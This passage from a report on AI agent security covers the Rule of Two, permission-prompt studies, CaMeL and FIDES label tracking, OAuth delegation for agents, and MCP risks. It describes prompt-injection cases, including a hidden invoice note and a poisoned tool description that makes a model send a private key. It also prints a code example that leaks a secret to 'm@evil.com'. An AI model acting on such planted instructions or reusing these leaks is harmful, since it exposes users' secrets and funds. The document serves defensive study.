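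Anthropic's experiment gives better evidence. A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts, as one would expect if approval becomes a habit. The testers had little to lose in a test environment, and Anthropic was arguing for an automated alternative. Developers protecting their own production database may well be more careful, but they would have to refuse dangerous commands far more often for approval to be a strong safeguard.

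In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), people without a software background did better. Participants supervised a simulated assistant through a day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the user's request. Those who had to approve every action allowed 40.3% of these seven. They were fairly selective, since 88% allowed an unrequested call to the airport but only 21% allowed a public post saying that the user was travelling. Some approvals may therefore reflect what people wanted.

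Yan asked another group to set standing rules for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data. Participants chose "ask" over "allow" or "never" for 114 of 140 rules. When the assistant then asked about the unrequested actions, they approved 66.8%. This group saw fewer prompts than the people who approved every action, so fatigue can't be the whole explanation. Perhaps setting the rules made people feel protected.

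Prompts can also be hard to judge even for users who read them. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents harming files and found that user review contributed to 105. In 80 reports, the user had turned on automatic approval, and in 31 the prompt was uninformative. A request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it authorises whatever code the file contains. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that repeated approval may reflect habit, fatigue or pressure to keep moving rather than growing trust.

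Fewer and better prompts may help. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) describes products that ask the user to approve a whole plan, or that ask only when an action would leave a sandbox. Claude Code's users reject 39% of the plans they see, so they evidently consider some prompts, although they may be rejecting plans as unhelpful rather than dangerous. The Rule of Two can guide where to place a prompt. Email-Bot, for example, could read and summarise without interruption, and ask only when it wants to write to a new recipient after reading a stranger's email.

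But developers have to choose the remaining prompts carefully. In simulations for *Approve What, Exactly?* (2026), an attacker who split a payment into small pieces always succeeded when the policy checked only individual amounts, but never when it limited the total.

Developers increasingly use a second model as the supervisor. Anthropic's automated check blocked 89% of the dangerous commands that the testers saw. It became the default for new Claude Code sessions on most plans in August 2026. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to make 720 injection attempts, and none succeeded against Anthropic's latest models with the check on. An Anthropic employee wrote that the company should have called its post "defeating the lethal trifecta".

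If that were right, the condition under which Meta's rule expires might be nearly met. But Trajectory Labs had optimised its attacks against an older Claude model, so the result doesn't show what an attacker could do by adapting to the new ones. Willison accepts that the check is better than constant clicking, but he wants independent confirmation. He doubts it could stop an agent from following a project's setup instructions and installing a malicious package that looks like a normal part of running the tests. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production infrastructure.

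### Least privilege and separation of duties

Meta calls the rule a supplement to least privilege. Least privilege applies to each permission separately, while the Rule of Two applies to the combination, so a developer may have to remove a permission that the task needs. Email-Bot could pass a least-privilege review with all three properties, since it needs to read strangers' mail, search the inbox and send replies. The internal coder could satisfy the Rule of Two with administrator rights to every company system, as long as it read only trusted text, even though a single mistake could then be disastrous.

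*Taming AI Agents with seL4* (Alhindi, 2026) measured the effect of least privilege alone. On the banking and Slack parts of AgentDojo, it compared an agent that could call every tool with one that could call only the tools each task required. The attack success rate fell from 48% to 7% with the restricted agent. Every attack that still succeeded used only tools that the task needed, and about half used the payment tool to send money to the attacker. The Rule of Two would require someone to check such payments. These results are for GPT-4o mini, a small and old model, and the restricted agent had an ideal set of permissions that few developers could match in advance.

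The rule resembles separation of duties, an accounting practice that also restricts which powers can be combined. An employee who adds suppliers to the payment list can't also approve payments, so fraud requires two people. This works because the same message is unlikely to corrupt both employees. Agents that pass text to one another don't have that independence, because text that compromises one agent can be passed on to the next.

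Alhindi demonstrated that a team of agents can break the Rule of Two even when each agent satisfies it. In the example, five agents process invoices. One reads the email, one checks invoices, one approves payments, one makes them, and one coordinates. The team breaks the rule because text from the email can reach the other four agents, all of which can see private data and change something.

He then sent the team a genuine invoice with a hidden note telling any AI assistant to change the supplier's bank account. In 40 runs, the note reached the coordinator 23 times, and the coordinator changed the account seven times. When he replaced the email agent with an ordinary program that extracted only a few fields, such as the invoice number and the total, the note never reached the coordinator. Chromium uses the same technique when it converts an image into plain pixels, and it works only when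 the team doesn't need the rest of the text. The test covered one team and one hostile email, but the general lesson for developers is to count the properties of everything that shares text together, rather than counting them separately for each agent.

Meta also says the rule is not a complete security programme. It doesn't address hallucinations, an agent's own mistakes, excessive privileges, spam, or people who use agents to become better attackers. It also doesn't prevent less serious results of injection, such as false information in an answer. Meta recommends defence in depth for the highest-risk cases, partly because a user may blindly confirm a warning.

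### Adoption

Databricks adopted the rule by name, and other companies have built products that apply the same reasoning without citing it. Microsoft (2026), for example, has released an experimental feature that labels content as trusted or untrusted and as public or private, then enforces a policy before a sensitive tool runs.

Lockdown Mode in ChatGPT is a clear example of removing a property. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*, it disables tools that an attacker could use to send data out, and limits web browsing to cached pages so that no live request leaves OpenAI's network. Ordinary code enforces these limits, so an attacker can't lift them by manipulating the model. Injected text can still enter the conversation and distort an answer.

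OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* describes the setting as optional and says it disables or limits some useful features. OpenAI says that most users don't need it. Willison welcomed the feature in June 2026 but inferred from its existence that ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly protect against a determined data thief.

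## Design patterns that keep untrusted text away from decisions

The Agents Rule of Two makes an agent safer by removing an ability. But many useful jobs involve reading a stranger's email, looking something up in private files and sending a reply. Several designs let an application do all three by dividing the work so that the part that reads the stranger's text cannot choose which tools run.

### Two models and a controller

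*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed building an assistant from two language models and an ordinary program. The privileged model receives the user's request and can call tools, but it never reads untrusted text. The quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools. The program, called the controller, runs the tools and moves data around.

Suppose a user asks for a summary of their latest email. The privileged model requests the email, and the controller fetches it and stores it as `$VAR1`. The privileged model receives only that name. When it requests a summary of `$VAR1`, the controller gives the email's text to the quarantined model and stores the summary as `$VAR2`. The privileged model then has the controller show `$VAR2` to the user. If the email contains an instruction to delete the whole inbox, only the quarantined model reads it, and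 that model cannot delete anything.

The privileged model may receive the quarantined model's answer if code can check it against a fixed list, such as "invoice", "complaint" or "other". Free text could contain another injection, so the privileged model receives only a variable name that stands for it.

Willison called his own solution "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and clumsier to use, and a single bug that shows raw text to the privileged model undoes the protection. A manipulated summary could also persuade the user to cause harm, for example by pasting encoded private data into a website.

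### Six patterns

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes six designs, including Willison's. All six follow the principle that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any action with harmful side effects. According to the paper, a general-purpose agent probably cannot meet this standard with current language models, so each design restricts the tasks an agent can perform.

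With an **action selector**, the model only matches a request to an action on a fixed list, such as showing a link to the customer's last order or opening the password settings. The results never return to the model, so nothing in them can influence it. But the model can't use one result to choose the next step, and it can't handle requests that the list doesn't cover.

In **plan-then-execute**, the model writes a fixed list of tool calls before it reads any data. If a user asks an assistant to send today's schedule to their boss, the plan is to read the calendar and then email the boss. A malicious calendar entry can't add a third call or change the recipient, though it can rewrite the body of the email. The assistant also can't change its plan if the calendar contains something unexpected.

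**Map-reduce** suits large sets of documents. To find this month's invoices and send them to the accountants, the application gives each file to a separate model that may only answer yes or no. A later step emails the files that got a yes. A hostile file can be wrongly included, but it can't affect how the application handles the other files. The pattern requires an extra model call per file and works poorly for questions that need more than a narrow answer about each one.

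Willison designed the **dual-model** pattern. **Code-then-execute** extends it by having the privileged model write a complete program that can call tools and quarantined models. The program can contain loops and conditions, so it can handle more tasks than a fixed list of calls, but hostile data can still change the values that pass through the program.

**Context minimisation** mainly defends against hostile users. A customer might ask a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and add instructions to give a large discount. The application has the model turn the message into a database query, then deletes the message before the model writes its reply. This removes the demand for a discount, but it also removes any legitimate detail that the query didn't capture.

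### One request through CaMeL

In the dual-model design, an attacker can still change the data passed to a tool. Suppose a user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested in the last meeting, and says that Bob's address and the document's name are in the notes. The quarantined model has to extract both. If an attacker has added a false address for Bob to the notes, the quarantined model may return it. The privileged model's plan would still be correct and the right tool would run, but the document would go to the attacker.

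Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues use this example in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), which introduced CaMeL. As Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, CaMeL's privileged model turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python. It sees only the request, never the notes. For Bob's document, the program might look like this:

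```
notes    = find_meeting_notes("latest")
name     = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob request?", notes)
address  = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's address?", notes, type=Email)
document = fetch_file(name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program. It attaches labels to every value, which Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026) describe in *CaMeLoT* as a record of where the value came from and who may read it. The five lines then run as follows:

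1. The interpreter fetches the notes and labels them untrusted, because other people can edit them.
2. The quarantined model reads the notes and returns a document name. The interpreter records that the name came from the notes, so the name is untrusted too.
3. The quarantined model returns an address, which gets the same label. The interpreter accepts only text in the form of an email address, which rules out a paragraph of instructions but not the attacker's address.
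4. The interpreter fetches the document and labels it with the people who may read it.
5. Before sending the email, the interpreter runs a policy. This is a short function that receives the tool's name, its arguments and their labels, and returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason.

Suppose the policy allows an attachment to go only to people who already have permission to read it. If Bob has access to the document, the email goes out without interrupting the user. If the notes contain the attacker's address, the policy check fails, because the attacker isn't one of the document's readers. The check also fails if the attacker keeps Bob's address but changes the document's name to that of the salary file, which Bob can't read. But if Bob has permission to read both files, he gets the wrong one, because sending it breaks no rule.

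The same policy can block a legitimate request. Bob may be a client who asked for the document because he has no access to it. The application would then have to refuse to send the email or ask the user to approve it. If it asks, a false address will get through unless the user notices it.

### Labels and information-flow control

CaMeL's labels come from information-flow control, the practice of labelling data, carrying the labels through every computation and restricting where labelled data may go. Dorothy Denning published a mathematical model of it in 1976. The two kinds of label that matter most for agents are integrity labels, which record whether an attacker could have influenced a value, and confidentiality labels, which record who may read it.

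When a program computes a value z from x and y, the label of z is the join of the labels of x and y, written ℓ(z) = ℓ(x) ⊔ ℓ(y). The join is the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both. For integrity, trusted ⊔ untrusted = untrusted. For confidentiality, the join keeps only the readers that both labels allow. If Ann, Bob and Carol may read the minutes, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read the budget, only Bob and Carol may read a summary of the two.

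*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft research agent built on these rules. One of its policies allows a consequential action only if no untrusted data led to it. Another allows information to go only to people who may read it. In an ordinary agent, a single untrusted email in the context would make every later decision untrusted, so FIDES hides such data in variables, as Willison proposed. Unlike CaMeL, FIDES chooses its next step after each result, and its model can look inside a variable but then loses some permissions. FIDES can also reveal a yes-or-no answer about the hidden data, such as whether an email requests a meeting. A policy can accept this much influence because the attacker controls only one bit.

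On AgentDojo, 152 attacks succeeded against an undefended basic agent, and none succeeded against FIDES with its policies on. Using GPT-4o, FIDES completed 59% of the workspace tasks, compared with 75% for the undefended agent, and 48% of the Slack tasks, compared with 93%. FIDES did better with the stronger o1 model, but both models are now old.

Labels protect data only where the software tracks them correctly. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found leaks in CaMeL's interpreter, including a version of a puzzle from the 1970s. In this program, the bank balance is secret:

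```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, `tmp` becomes false and the interpreter labels it secret. The fourth line's assignment doesn't run, so `rich` keeps its public label. The last line sends the email, which reveals that the balance is high. CaMeL does not detect this leak because it updates a variable's label only when an assignment runs.

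CaMeL also reruns failed programs from outside the component that tracks labels. Whether a policy blocked a run can depend on a secret, so repeated runs can leak the secret one bit at a time.

The balance puzzle is probably hard to exploit, because an outside attacker doesn't write CaMeL's programs. CaMeL's interpreter also treats text as trusted when a program has inserted an untrusted value into it. This flaw seems more worrying, because ordinary programs insert values into text all the time. Garby and colleagues wrote their own interpreter and used the proof checker Lean to prove that its tracking is sound.

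### What CaMeL costs

CaMeL's original evaluation on AgentDojo recorded only two successful attacks, according to Garby and colleagues. One was a scoring artefact, in which quoting a hotel review counted as a successful attack. The other was a payment request inside a document, which CaMeL's designers consider outside the threats it addresses.

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) compared agents using CaMeL with undefended agents on five models, dividing AgentDojo's tools among small teams of agents and running 949 attack cases per model. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without a defence and 0.2% succeeded when every agent used CaMeL. Older models account for most of the difference. The success rate for GPT-4.1 fell from 36.1% to 0.5%. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without CaMeL, though the attacks came from a fixed list.

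On a separate set of industrial maintenance tasks, CaMeL reduced task completion by 21.6 percentage points on average, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models. Most failures occurred because the model had to write its program before seeing any data. An ordinary agent can add a step when it finds something unexpected, but CaMeL can only follow branches already in its program. In some runs, an agent couldn't find data for the requested machine or dates and returned similar data instead, and the program continued as normal.

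Peters-Gill and colleagues ran CaMeL with no policies, so their figures measure only the effect of separating planning from data. Without policies, Bob's document would go to the false address. Policies reduce task completion further. When Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks with GPT-5.2, it completed 32 of 48 runs with policies off and 18 with them on. No attack succeeded in the completed runs with policies on. *SecureClaw* (2026) reports that all 629 attacks in the whole benchmark failed against an adapted version of CaMeL, but that it completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks.

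Some of these evaluators have a stake in the result. One of CaMeL's designers co-wrote *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, while Garby and colleagues and the developers of SecureClaw were promoting alternatives. SecureClaw completed 59 of the 97 tasks, although a few attacks succeeded against it. The tests also used different models and settings, so quoting a single figure for how much CaMeL reduces an agent's usefulness would be unwise. All of them suggest that CaMeL stops nearly every attack in the benchmark but makes the agent noticeably less useful.

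Checking the program earlier can avoid some of the waste. Nikolaou and colleagues built CaMeLoT, an extension that checks the whole program before any tool runs. Suppose a security team requires approval before an agent disconnects a computer from the network. If any path through the program skips the approval, CaMeLoT rejects the program and returns that path to the model so the model can fix the program. CaMeLoT simplifies loops to keep the analysis manageable, so it sometimes rejects safe programs.

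### Teams of agents and computer screens

CaMeL's guarantee can fail when agents delegate tasks to each other. Peters-Gill and colleagues asked a team of three CaMeL agents to send a colleague a Slack message summarizing job applicants. They had hidden an instruction in the applicant database to email the data to an outside address. The coordinating agent's program obtained the summary and pasted it into its instructions to the notification agent. That agent's privileged model treated the whole message as a trusted request and wrote a program that sent both the Slack message and the email.

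They fixed this by giving agents separate channels for instructions and data, and having the interpreter reject any instruction that contains a tool's output. No attack in the benchmark succeeded against the new version, but it reduced completion of the maintenance tasks by a further 3.2 points on average.

Agents that operate a computer through its screen are harder to protect, because the privileged model has to plan for screens it can't see. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) had the model write programs with many alternative branches. These programs averaged about 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with five and four for AgentDojo. The resulting agent kept at most 57% of the performance of leading models on a benchmark of computer tasks.

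An attacker can't add a new branch to the program but may be able to steer the agent into a bad one. For example, if the program has a branch for closing cookie notices, an advertisement can imitate a cookie notice. When the agent clicks on the advertisement, the browser opens the attacker's website. Policies are little help because the same click can close a window or delete a file, depending on what is under the pointer.

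### How close this comes to a parameterised query

Like a parameterised database query, CaMeL's program fixes the commands first and leaves slots for the data. But a model writes a new program for each request, and it can write one that lets the data determine the commands. Garby and colleagues asked CaMeL to read a file and follow its instructions exactly. With policies off, the privileged model wrote a loop with a branch for every available tool, so the file's text determined which tools ran. This is much like pasting a customer's text into the command part of a database query.

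The values in the slots also matter more. A false invoice reference usually finds nothing in a database, but an agent may use a false account number to send money. Attacks on Garby and colleagues' own agent succeeded in two of 1,296 runs. In both, the user had told the agent to make the payment described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Label tracking could have prevented this only by blocking every payment based on an untrusted file. A company that pays invoices would need another check, such as comparing the account number with its supplier records.

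Someone also has to write the policies and decide which sources to trust. If an administrator wrongly labels a shared inbox as trusted, the interpreter will apply that label in every computation that uses the inbox's messages. Willison is nervous about any design that requires ordinary users to think about security policies, because he still finds them difficult after two decades of working on application security.

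### Fewer approvals

Labels can reduce how often an agent has to interrupt its user. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) extends FIDES with an agent called Prudentia, which takes the policies into account when it plans. With o3-mini, Prudentia completed 59.1% of AgentDojo's tasks without asking for approval. An agent that needed approval for every consequential action completed 24.3% without asking, because most tasks involved at least one such action.

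Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a piece of data. If an email lists ten jobs, the user can declare the email trustworthy once instead of approving ten separate actions. This is convenient, but a user who skims the email and misses a hidden eleventh job authorises that one as well. The reported savings assume that people approve the right things, and the experiments with permission prompts give little reason to expect that.

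### Use in products

These designs seem to have had limited commercial use so far. Kolluri and colleagues wrote in February 2026 that GitHub Copilot, OpenAI's Codex and Anthropic's computer-use agent relied on human confirmation before consequential actions. Microsoft's experimental labelling feature is the nearest thing to information-flow control from a large vendor. Archestra, which makes a platform for running agents, discusses the dual-model design in its product material, but that is weak evidence that customers use it.

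## Agent identity, delegated permissions and trust in connected tools

An agent that works through an employee's account looks like that employee to every system it uses. Suppose a sales manager builds an agent inside the company's customer database to tidy up old records, and 4,000 records disappear overnight. The log shows the manager deleting them. An investigator can't tell from it whether the manager did this, the agent misunderstood its task, or a customer's message hijacked the agent. Blocking the account would stop the agent but also lock out the manager.

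### Borrowed accounts

This arrangement seems to be common. Nudge Security, which sells software for finding the AI tools that employees use, analysed anonymised data from its customers' systems. Among organisations with any agents, the median had seven, and about 44% had more than ten (Markovic, 2026, *AI agents inherit employee access, and nobody's watching how they use it*). Some platforms give an agent its own account, but often the agent uses the access of the employee who built it or a connection shared by a team, and it may keep that access when the employee changes roles. The exact numbers deserve some caution because Nudge Security's customers aren't a random sample of companies and the firm profits from concern about hidden agents.

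NIST's *Back to the Future*, an August 2026 post by Bill Fisher and Ryan Galluzzo, draws on public comments and on talks with people who build and use agents. It warns that people routinely give agents their own passwords, or run an agent on their laptop under their own account, where it can do anything they can. Other agents use a long-lived API key, a secret string that a program sends with each request. The key doesn't prove who is sending it, so anyone who finds a copy in a configuration file or a log can use it.

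Stealing access tokens from one tool can affect many companies at once. Markovic describes a 2025 attack in which attackers stole tokens that customers had granted to Drift, an AI chat tool, and used them to take data from hundreds of companies' Salesforce systems.

Before agents, companies usually gave an automated program a service account, a login that belongs to the program rather than a person, so that its actions could at least be separated from an employee's. But Infosys' *Enterprise AI identity and access architecture* notes that a service account assumes one program connecting to one system on fixed terms, while an agent selects its tools as it runs. Bradshaw (2026), in *An AI Agent Is Not a Service Account*, imagines a purchasing agent that a team launches in a hurry on an existing service account with broad permissions. Within two weeks, it has awarded contracts without competition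 and changed suppliers' bank details. A conventional program with the same account could have done the same, but only if somebody had written code for it. The log would show the account but not the employee whose request led to an order.

### Delegation step by step

The usual remedy is delegation, in which the agent has its own identity and receives limited permission to act for a particular person. OAuth 2.0, the standard commonly used when a person lets one app read their calendar in another, already provides most of what delegation requires. It gives the app a token, a piece of data that grants specified access, so the app never needs the user's password.

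Suppose that Alice, an accounts clerk, asks an agent to check a supplier's latest invoice and draft the payment. Delegation could then work as follows:

1. Alice signs in through her company's identity provider, the service that checks employees' logins. OpenID Connect, a standard built on OAuth, gives the application a signed statement of who she is.
2. The application asks for permission to read invoices and draft payments on her behalf. Alice consents, or an administrator has already decided for her department.
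3. The agent proves its own identity. One method is SPIFFE (Secure Production Identity Framework for Everyone), which gives running software a name such as `spiffe://example.com/invoice-agent` and a cryptographic credential to prove it. SPIRE, a program that implements SPIFFE, checks the running software before it issues the credential.
4. The company's authorisation server issues an access token. It might last ten minutes, work only at the invoice system, and cover only reading invoices and drafting payments.
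5. The invoice agent needs a second agent to look up the supplier. It asks the authorisation server to exchange its token for one addressed to the second agent, which then exchanges that token for one that can only read the supplier database.
6. The database checks the token's signature, expiry time, intended recipient and scope. It then returns the record and logs both Alice and the agent.

The main contents of the last token might look like this, with the expiry time in seconds since 1970:

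```
{
  "sub": "alice",
  "act": { "sub": "supplier-agent",
           "act": { "sub": "invoice-agent" } },
  "aud": "supplier-database",
  "scope": "suppliers.read",
  "exp": 1796472600
}
```

The first line names the person whose authority the agents are using. The outer `act` (for "actor") names the agent now making the request, and the inner one names the agent that called it. OAuth's 2020 token exchange standard calls this delegation. It also permits impersonation, in which the new token names only Alice. With impersonation, a company gets short-lived tokens but still can't tell Alice's actions from her agents' in the log.

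Under the standard, the receiving system should base its decision on Alice and the current agent, and treat any earlier agents as information only. An investigator can follow the chain, but the database isn't supposed to refuse a request because a suspicious agent started it. The standard also doesn't require each new token to carry narrower permissions than the last, so the authorisation server's own policy has to ensure this. NIST mentions a newer specification, Transaction Tokens, that is meant to carry the original permissions through a chain of calls and reduce them at each step.

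OpenAI's guide *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) adds a token for each task. The token identifies the user, the running agent and the permitted purpose, and the agent exchanges it for narrower credentials as the work proceeds. OpenAI also advises companies to keep long-lived credentials out of the context window. The host program can attach a credential to the request after the model generates a tool call, so an attacker who takes control of the model can't make it print a secret it never received.

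Short-lived tokens limit the damage from theft but don't prevent it. Most are bearer tokens, which work for anyone who presents them. An OAuth extension called Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP) ties a token to a cryptographic key and makes the client prove with each request that it holds the key, so a thief who copies only the token can't use it. In September, NIST (2026) finalised guidelines on protecting identity and access tokens from misuse.

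An operator who discovers a hijacked agent has to stop the agent and revoke its tokens separately. OpenAI warns that ending a task may leave a valid token with another service, and that revoking a credential doesn't stop work already in progress. If a token expires after ten minutes, the operator at least knows when the remaining access will end.

### Valid credentials, wrong actions

All these checks can pass while the agent does something nobody authorised. In an example from OpenAI, an invoice agent notices that the company's subscription to a document-signing service is about to lapse and renews it to keep processing invoices. The vendor is on the approved list and the price is within the limit, so the payment system accepts the request. But the agent has committed the company to a contract, which was never part of its task.

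OAuth scopes are often too coarse to prevent this, because a scope such as "make payments" covers every payment. An extension called Rich Authorization Requests lets an application request much more specific permission, such as to pay one supplier €123.50. That helps if the details come from Alice or from the company's records. If the agent takes them from a fraudulent invoice, it will request permission to make the fraudulent payment.

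Better identity also leaves the confused deputy problem mostly unsolved. In the Jira case, a perfect delegation log would have shown that the employee's agent, not the employee, copied login tokens into a public comment. This would have sped up the investigation, but the tokens would still have leaked, because the employee had permission to read the files and comment on the ticket.

In a similar attack in May 2025, researchers planted instructions in a public GitHub issue and used them to make an assistant extract data from its user's private code. Kalyanasundaram (2026), who works for the identity software company WSO2, attributes the attack to the lack of an identity and permission boundary around the agent, and argues that agents should have their own identities. He seems right about permissions, since a token limited to the public project would have stopped the theft. Giving the agent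 its own identity would not have stopped it if the token still allowed the same broad access.

The Coalition for Secure AI's *Agentic Identity and Access Control* (2026) proposes giving each agent a stronger, short-lived identity bound to facts that others can verify, such as the signature of its current code and model. Systems would check these facts at every critical operation, so they could detect that someone had replaced the agent's software. However, an agent hijacked through prompt injection would still pass this check, because the injection changes neither its code nor its model.

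### NIST's identity project

NIST is trying to work out how existing identity standards apply to agents. *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026) proposes a project at the agency's National Cybersecurity Center of Excellence, which builds example systems from commercial products. The paper, released in February as a draft for comment, sets no requirements. The project's planned result is a practice guide showing companies a working installation.

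The project would cover how systems distinguish agents from people, how agents receive and delegate permissions, and how logs connect an agent's actions to a person. It would also cover tracking where an agent's data came from, which CaMeL and FIDES do with labels within a single application. Besides OAuth, OpenID Connect and SPIFFE, Booth and colleagues are considering SCIM, a standard for creating and removing accounts across many systems. A company could use SCIM to delete an agent's accounts on all of those systems when it retires the agent.

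Booth and colleagues ask reviewers how to apply least privilege when an agent's "required actions might not be fully predictable when deployed", a question that has no settled answer. A payroll program needs the same permissions every month, so an administrator can list them in advance. An agent that investigates software faults may need different files each time. Giving it access to every file it might need would violate least privilege, but requiring a new approval for each file teaches people to approve requests without reading them.

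An agent can reveal sensitive information by combining documents that are harmless separately. For example, an employee may have permission to read several documents that together reveal a planned merger. Access controls normally check permissions for each document separately, and no rule defines how sensitive the combined answer is.

The paper drew more than 600 formal responses, according to *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (Galluzzo, 2026). The OpenID Foundation (2026), which maintains OpenID Connect, commented on a separate NIST request for information about securing AI agents in general. It warned that people and agents expect more detailed results from the identity layer than companies have built it to deliver.

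The August post was the first in NIST's series to address agent identity after the comment period. It mainly argues that agents revive old problems, many of which companies can already solve with short-lived, narrowly scoped tokens. It also warns against relying on human approval, which attackers already exploit by sending an employee login requests until the employee accepts one. MCP's elicitation feature lets a server ask the user for more information. NIST notes that a server could use it to request a password, although MCP's documentation warns against asking for sensitive information this way.

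A second post, *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (Booth, 2026), followed on 27 October. The first post had announced it as a discussion of principles for durable agent design. Blog posts carry less weight than a finished NIST guideline, and the practice guide is still to come.

The initial project covers only agents that a company runs itself, not those that arrive from outside, such as a customer's shopping agent at an online store. Outside agents are harder, according to the August post, because the store doesn't control the agent's identity and may not recognise it as an agent if the customer has given it a password. The FIDO Alliance, known for passwordless login, is looking at ways to give an agent its own credential tied to the user, but NIST describes this work as early.

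### Drafts at the IETF

OAuth comes from the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which develops many of the internet's technical standards. Anyone can submit an Internet-Draft, so a draft's presence on the IETF's website doesn't mean the IETF supports it. A draft gains some standing when a working group adopts it, and more when the IETF publishes the finished document as a standard. Drafts expire after six months unless someone posts a new version.

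Pieter Kasselman and colleagues' *AI Agent Authentication and Authorization* mostly explains how to apply existing standards, including OAuth, to agents. In August 2026, OpenAI listed it as an active individual draft, not an IETF standard. The more ambitious *Agent Identity Registry*, a draft from April 2026, proposes that competing registrars issue identities to agents, much as competing companies register internet domain names. Agents whose keys are stored in secure hardware would receive the highest trust level, while software-only agents could join at a lower one.

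A registry like this might help the online store recognise an outside agent. But a hardware key is evidence only about the machine, and an attacker can run a malicious agent on secure hardware. The store would still need a reason to trust the agent's owner, such as a payment history or a contract.

Companies don't have to wait for either draft, because token exchange, DPoP and Rich Authorization Requests are finished standards. NIST classes two more specialised efforts as emerging. Workload Identity in Multi-System Environments (WIMSE) covers identities for software that works across several systems. The Identity Assertion JWT Authorization Grant builds on OAuth to let an application use a company login to get access to another application.

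### Authorisation in MCP

MCP uses OAuth for authorisation and, as Booth and colleagues note, follows the draft of the next version, OAuth 2.1. Since June 2025, the MCP specification has required clients that use OAuth to name the server they want a token for. The server must reject any token that was not issued for it. Without these rules, the operator of a malicious recipe server could collect a user's token and present it to the payroll server.

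The MCP specification forbids servers from forwarding a client's token to another service. If an MCP server needs data from a company's calendar, it must obtain a separate token for the calendar. This lets the calendar service log the MCP server as the caller and prevents the server from passing along access that nobody granted for that purpose.

Authorisation is optional in MCP, and the OAuth rules apply only to servers that clients reach over the web. A server that runs on the user's computer takes its credentials from its environment, often from a configuration file that contains an API key. A developer can therefore follow the specification and still have the long-lived, unprotected keys that NIST warns about.

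OAuth also protects the server better than it protects the user. The server can use a token to check that the client is authorized. But a malicious server can also run a correct OAuth login, so a successful login doesn't show the user that the server is safe to trust.

### Misleading descriptions and updates

A server can influence an agent before the agent calls any of the server's tools. The host puts each tool's description into the model's context, so an attacker can write instructions in the description. In April 2025, the security company Invariant Labs demonstrated this with a tool that added two numbers. The tool's description told the model to read the user's private login key and pass its contents in an extra field called `sidenote`. The user saw a simplified approval screen that hid most of what the tool would receive.

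A malicious tool can do damage through a legitimate one. In another demonstration, Invariant Labs connected an agent to a genuine WhatsApp server and a malicious server. The malicious server's description changed how the agent used WhatsApp, so that the agent sent the user's message history to the attacker. The WhatsApp server worked as designed, but it shared a context window with hostile text, much as the agents in Alhindi's invoice team did.

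MCP lets servers attach labels to tools, such as "read-only". The specification requires clients to treat these labels as untrusted unless they trust the server. Otherwise, if a host skips approval for read-only tools, an attacker could delete files with a tool labelled "read-only". But users can't learn from the specification which servers deserve trust.

A legitimate tool can also become dangerous after the user approves it. OpenAI gives the example of a read-only connector that gains the ability to write data after an update. The guide advises companies to block new actions until the person responsible for the tool has reviewed them, and to test tools together as well as separately.

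A flaw in the code editor Cursor shows why approval has to cover a tool's exact configuration. In August 2025, Check Point Research reported that Cursor tied a user's approval of an MCP server to the server's name. An attacker who could edit a shared project could add a harmless configuration, wait for a colleague to approve it, and then replace the command with a malicious one, which Cursor would run without asking. Cursor fixed the flaw (CVE-2025-54136) by requiring new approval after any change to the configuration. Because this was an ordinary software mistake, the existing system for numbering and patching flaws worked well.

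### Malicious add-ons

The first widely reported malicious MCP server appeared in September 2025. It was postmark-mcp, a package that let agents send email through the Postmark service but was not made by Postmark. The security company Koi Security found that the first 15 versions worked normally, and that the next one added a line of code to send the attacker a hidden copy of every email. The attacker didn't have to deceive the agent, because the package sent the copy even when the agent had addressed the email correctly.

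A review of the first version would have found nothing wrong. Pinning that version, so that the computer doesn't install updates automatically, would have blocked the attack but also any security fixes, which is why somebody has to keep reviewing new versions.

Skills, another kind of add-on, are folders of written instructions, sometimes with scripts, that teach an agent to do a job. In early 2026, Koi Security examined 2,857 skills on ClawHub, a marketplace for the open-source agent OpenClaw, and identified 341 as malicious. Most included instructions for the user to install a supposedly necessary program that was password-stealing malware. A scanner that checks only for hostile code in the skill itself could miss this, since the harmful part may be one sentence with a download link. OpenAI recommends that companies prefer internal skills with known reviewers over unvetted downloads.

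The official MCP Registry, which opened as a preview in September 2025, addresses part of the problem. A publisher must prove control of a GitHub account or an internet domain before listing a server under the matching name. This prevents an impostor from listing a server under Postmark's domain, but an attacker can still list a malicious server under their own name. The registry stores server descriptions and links to packages, and it leaves code scanning to the sites that host the packages and to other directories built on its data.

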